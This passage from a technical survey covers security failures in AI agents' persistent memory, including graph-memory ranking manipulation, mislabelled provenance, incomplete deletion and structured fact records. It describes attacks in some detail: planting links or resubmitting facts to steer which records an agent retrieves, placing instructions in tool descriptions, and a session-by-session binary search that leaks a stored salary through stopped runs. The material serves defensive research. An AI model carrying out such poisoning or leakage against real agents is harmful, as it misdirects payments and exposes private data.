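An agent's behaviour also depends on which memory entries its search leaves out. If the search returns five entries and Ana's note about January's wrong account number ranks sixth, the assistant will advise her without it. An attacker who can influence the ranking can therefore change the advice without showing the model any untrusted text.

*Selection Integrity for LLM Graph Memory* (Fei, Fei and colleagues, 2026) demonstrates this on memories that link records through the people and things they mention. One such system, HippoRAG2, starts from the people and things named in a question, spreads a score along the links, and returns the five highest-scoring records. In a shared memory, anyone who can add records can usually create new links too.

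In one example, an agent must pay whichever of two authors was born first. A compromised agent that shares the memory adds six links, which move an unrelated passage to the top of the results. The paying agent then pays the wrong author, even though it read only genuine records from trusted writers.

The attack succeeds if the new links bring a record enough score to overtake the last one selected. Let $\pi(s)$ be the score of an item $s$ named in the question, $\text{str}(s)$ the total weight of its existing links, and $W$ the weight of each new link. The extra score is approximately

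$$\kappa = (1-\alpha) \sum_s \pi(s)\, \frac{W}{W + \text{str}(s)}$$

where $\alpha$ is the chance of returning to the starting items at each step, which is one half in HippoRAG2. For one question, five new links added 0.00079 and the gap to fifth place was 0.00076, so the wrong record got in. An operator can calculate both numbers before any attack. On a graph that nobody had yet attacked, the predictions ranked the questions by vulnerability almost perfectly, with an AUROC of 0.99.

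A changed selection often does no harm. Six links changed the results for up to half of the questions that HippoRAG2 answered through its graph, but in the shared-memory test the agent misdirected only 14 of the 132 transfers it would otherwise have got right. Graphiti did worse in a mode that ranks facts by how often they have been mentioned. When another writer resubmitted a few of the user's own facts, the agent got 70% of 66 previously correct answers wrong. The test included only questions on which ten or fewer resubmissions were enough, so the rate for all questions would be lower.

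The attacker's influence here is an implicit flow, since it determines which records appear without adding anything to them. A tracker could catch it by labelling every result with everyone who had written to the graph, but that would cause extreme label creep. Fei and colleagues also tried discarding results close to suspicious links. Because the attacker's links lead to the user's own records, this discarded those records too, and the correct record remained in only 17% of attacked searches, compared with 50% with no defence.

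The proposed solution counts a writer's links only where they touch that writer's own records. It kept the correct record in 59% of attacked searches, the same as without an attack, and had no measurable effect on ordinary searches. The proof applies to the kind of ranking HippoRAG2 uses. An attacker can still attach thousands of new records to the items in a question so that little score reaches anything else. On the test memory, this would remove the correct record in at most 9.7% of searches.

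Planted notes can crowd out real ones when the assistant searches by similarity of wording, even though this kind of search has no links to manipulate. If the assistant fetches the five closest notes and then discards the untrusted ones, it is left with nothing when all five were planted. The software should exclude untrusted notes before it ranks the rest.

### Labels that are wrong from the start

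If Ana copies the supplier's page into the chat and asks for a summary, the system receives the text from Ana. TMA-NM would therefore save the false account number as something the user said, and the number would pass every later check.

The chat window could treat pasted text as untrusted until Ana confirms it, since software can usually distinguish pasting from typing. But she would then have to confirm even her own rules when she pasted them from a document, and the label would still be wrong if she retyped the number from the page.

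Tools present a similar problem. Louck suggests authenticating connections or signing responses, so that an attacker can't impersonate the bank's service, and raising an alert when a source's claimed identity doesn't match its authenticated one. But a service that an attacker has taken over can still sign its responses. Kim and colleagues, in their survey of attacks on agents, add that an attacker can put instructions in a tool's name or description, which the agent reads before it calls the tool.

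A tool that works as intended can also return text written by a stranger. A list of bank transactions, for example, includes payment references written by whoever sent the money. If the tool is on the approved list and Ana asks for this week's transactions, TMA-NM would treat those references as trusted text. To prevent this, the operator would have to leave the tool off the list or label that field separately.

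When a wrong label on an original entry is corrected, the system also has to find the notes derived from that entry and recalculate their labels.

### One bit per session

Garby and colleagues proved a noninterference theorem that allows a run to reveal one bit by stopping. If memory keeps the secret available between sessions, twenty sessions can reveal twenty bits. This is an inference from the theory, and no one has reported such an attack.

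Suppose someone using Ana's account wants to know Ben's salary. They ask the agent to prepare a budget and take a forbidden step if the salary is above €64,000, then see whether the system stops the run. In each later session, they test the middle of the remaining range. Seven sessions are enough to identify a salary below €128,000 to within €1,000. This works only because the salary stays in memory after Ben's session ends. CaMeL's retry loop allows the same kind of search within one task.

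After the first stopped run, the system could block all further requests that touch the salary until a person has reviewed that run. This would limit the leak to which of the twenty sessions stopped, if any. That gives 21 possible outcomes, or at most $\log_2 21 \approx 4.4$ bits. But an attacker could trigger a block on purpose to keep Ana from doing legitimate work.

Approval checks can leak in the same way. *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (2026) describes a separate model that compares a proposed output with the protected records and returns only "SAFE" or "BLOCKED", because an explanation could reveal something about the records. Each answer therefore reveals at most one bit, but an agent with persistent memory may request hundreds of answers. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* suggests labels that record how much information an output carries about its sources. A memory system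 could add up these amounts for each secret and refuse further outputs once the total reaches a limit. The amounts are simple to count for yes-or-no answers but much harder to estimate for a paragraph.

Small influences on trusted data also add up. In the earlier sorting example, if the assistant saves the endorsed category of each email, twenty emails at three bits each give sixty bits. That is enough to encode an 18-digit number, although a trusted program would have to assemble it.

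### Deleting an entry and everything made from it

When Ana learns that the supplier's page was false, she can delete Monday's note, but the weekly summary may still contain the account number. The same problem arises if Ben asks the assistant to forget his salary.

In *AfterDeleteBench*, Saleh, Nahavandi and colleagues (2026) tested whether an agent could still reveal a secret after the original record was deleted. They gave the agent a made-up secret, let the software build a summary, deleted the record and asked for the secret. Qwen2.5-7B returned it in 68% of cases, and never in matched tests where the agent hadn't received it. The summary was just the joined text of the records, so it was bound to contain the secret. In a second test, only the secret's three parts and a public rule for combining them survived. Three models reconstructed the secret in 62% to 99% of cases.

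A system that records each summary's sources, or lineage, can find the affected summaries and rebuild them from the remaining sources. This reduced recovery to zero in the settings Saleh and colleagues tested, where the record was complete, but real records may have gaps. *MemShift* (2026) warns that revoking consent for derived entries requires knowing what they depend on, and that a log of what the system read only approximates this.

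Ameur and colleagues use the cautious record, which counts everything in the writer's context as a parent. Their system, LinEra, encrypts every entry and calculates the key for a derived entry $c$ from the keys of its parents $p_1, \dots, p_m$ and a value $r_c$ of its own:

$$k_c = H(k_{p_1}, \dots, k_{p_m}, r_c)$$

To forget Monday's note, LinEra destroys the information needed to calculate that note's key. The keys of the weekly summary, and of everything made from the summary, then can't be calculated either. The system doesn't have to find these entries, and old backups of them become unreadable too.

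The researchers planted 71 secrets, such as door codes, in the ten conversations and then asked for their deletion. They assumed an attacker who later obtained every file and the current keys. The secret or its topic was still recoverable in 70 cases after ordinary deletion, in 67 when each entry was encrypted under an independent key, and in none with LinEra. A version of LinEra that recorded only the three most similar texts as parents still revealed the topic of 13 secrets, so estimating which texts influenced an entry is risky for deletion as well.

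Label creep determines how much other memory becomes unreadable. With session-level summaries, forgetting 1% of the messages cut the agent's answer score from 27.8 to 13.8. The score rose to 27.9 after the model rewrote the lost summaries from the surviving messages, which took 19 minutes on one graphics processor for 169 sessions.

Neither method removes information that another source repeats. If Ben mentioned his salary in two messages, forgetting one leaves the salary in the other. *Stashbird* (2026) records which episodes support each fact. When an episode is deleted, the system keeps any fact that another episode still supports, and it withholds affected summaries until it has regenerated them. This is sensible for honest data, but if an attacker planted the account number in two places, removing it would require finding both.

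Removing a poisoned entry also doesn't necessarily undo its effects on other entries. Fei and colleagues found that Graphiti marks a fact as expired when somebody contradicts it but doesn't record whose message caused this, so deleting the message later wouldn't lead the system to restore the fact. Lineage therefore has to cover changes to old entries as well as the sources of new ones. The 435 works that Ding and colleagues reviewed focused more on accumulating and retrieving information than on recovering from errors or discarding information.

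### Replacing prose with structured records

Several of these problems become easier if the agent stores separate facts instead of paragraphs. Zahn and Chana (2026), in *Facts as First-Class Objects*, propose records with four fields: a subject, a property, a value and the source. Monday's note would become

| Subject | Property | Value | Source |
|---|---|---|---|
| Supplier | bank account | X | supplier's web page, Monday |

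Software can copy this record without a model rewriting it, so the label doesn't spread and the source isn't lost. Deleting the record removes the fact unless a model has already used it in a summary. Looking up "supplier, bank account" returns every matching record, so planted notes can't push one out of the results.

In Zahn and Chana's tests, a summary of 2,000 facts preserved 40% of them, while the structured records preserved them all. Of 20 project rules, such as deploying only in Europe, 91% remained after one round of compaction and 46% after three. When facts had almost identical wording, similarity search ranked the right one first only 20% of the time, but exact matching on the structured records' fields always did.

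The 2,000 facts were drug measurements that already fitted the format, so the tests don't show how reliably a model can convert Ana's emails into such records. A model that has read the supplier's page could also put a false value in the record for another supplier. The software therefore has to fill in the source field itself and count everything the model read while extracting the value as a source. The record also becomes prose again if its value field may contain any sentence, such as "phone before paying, unless the change is small".

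### What better engineering can remove

One way to sort these failures is by whether they would still occur if the memory held only structured records with fixed types of value.

| Failure | Would it remain? | What could reduce it |
|---|---|---|
| Steered search results | yes, if links or popularity affect ranking | exact lookup, or limits on whose links count |
| Wrong origin labels | yes | authenticated channels, marks on pasted text |
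| Leaks of one bit per session | yes | blocks after a stopped run, running totals |
| Incomplete deletion | only if the lineage has gaps | complete lineage, linked encryption keys |
| Label creep | much less | small contexts, rewriting without the untrusted source |
| Facts that decide actions | yes, but the deciding fields would be known | checks on each value and on what triggered the step |

The first four are mostly engineering problems, and databases and operating systems have versions of them. Better software could remove gaps in lineage and many ways of steering a search, keep leaks small, and make wrong labels rarer, but it can't determine whether an honest source is mistaken.

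Label creep occurs in prose memory because no code shows which parts of a model's note depend on which sources, so the note has to carry the restrictions of everything in the model's context. Giving the model less context reduces the number of notes affected, but a summary that draws on many sources must still carry all their restrictions unless someone declassifies it.

Free text also makes it impossible to list in advance which sentences will affect which actions. A database designer knows that the account field decides where payments go and can require approval to change it. In a page of notes, a sentence like "the supplier was very helpful last time" may lead the assistant to recommend a larger order.
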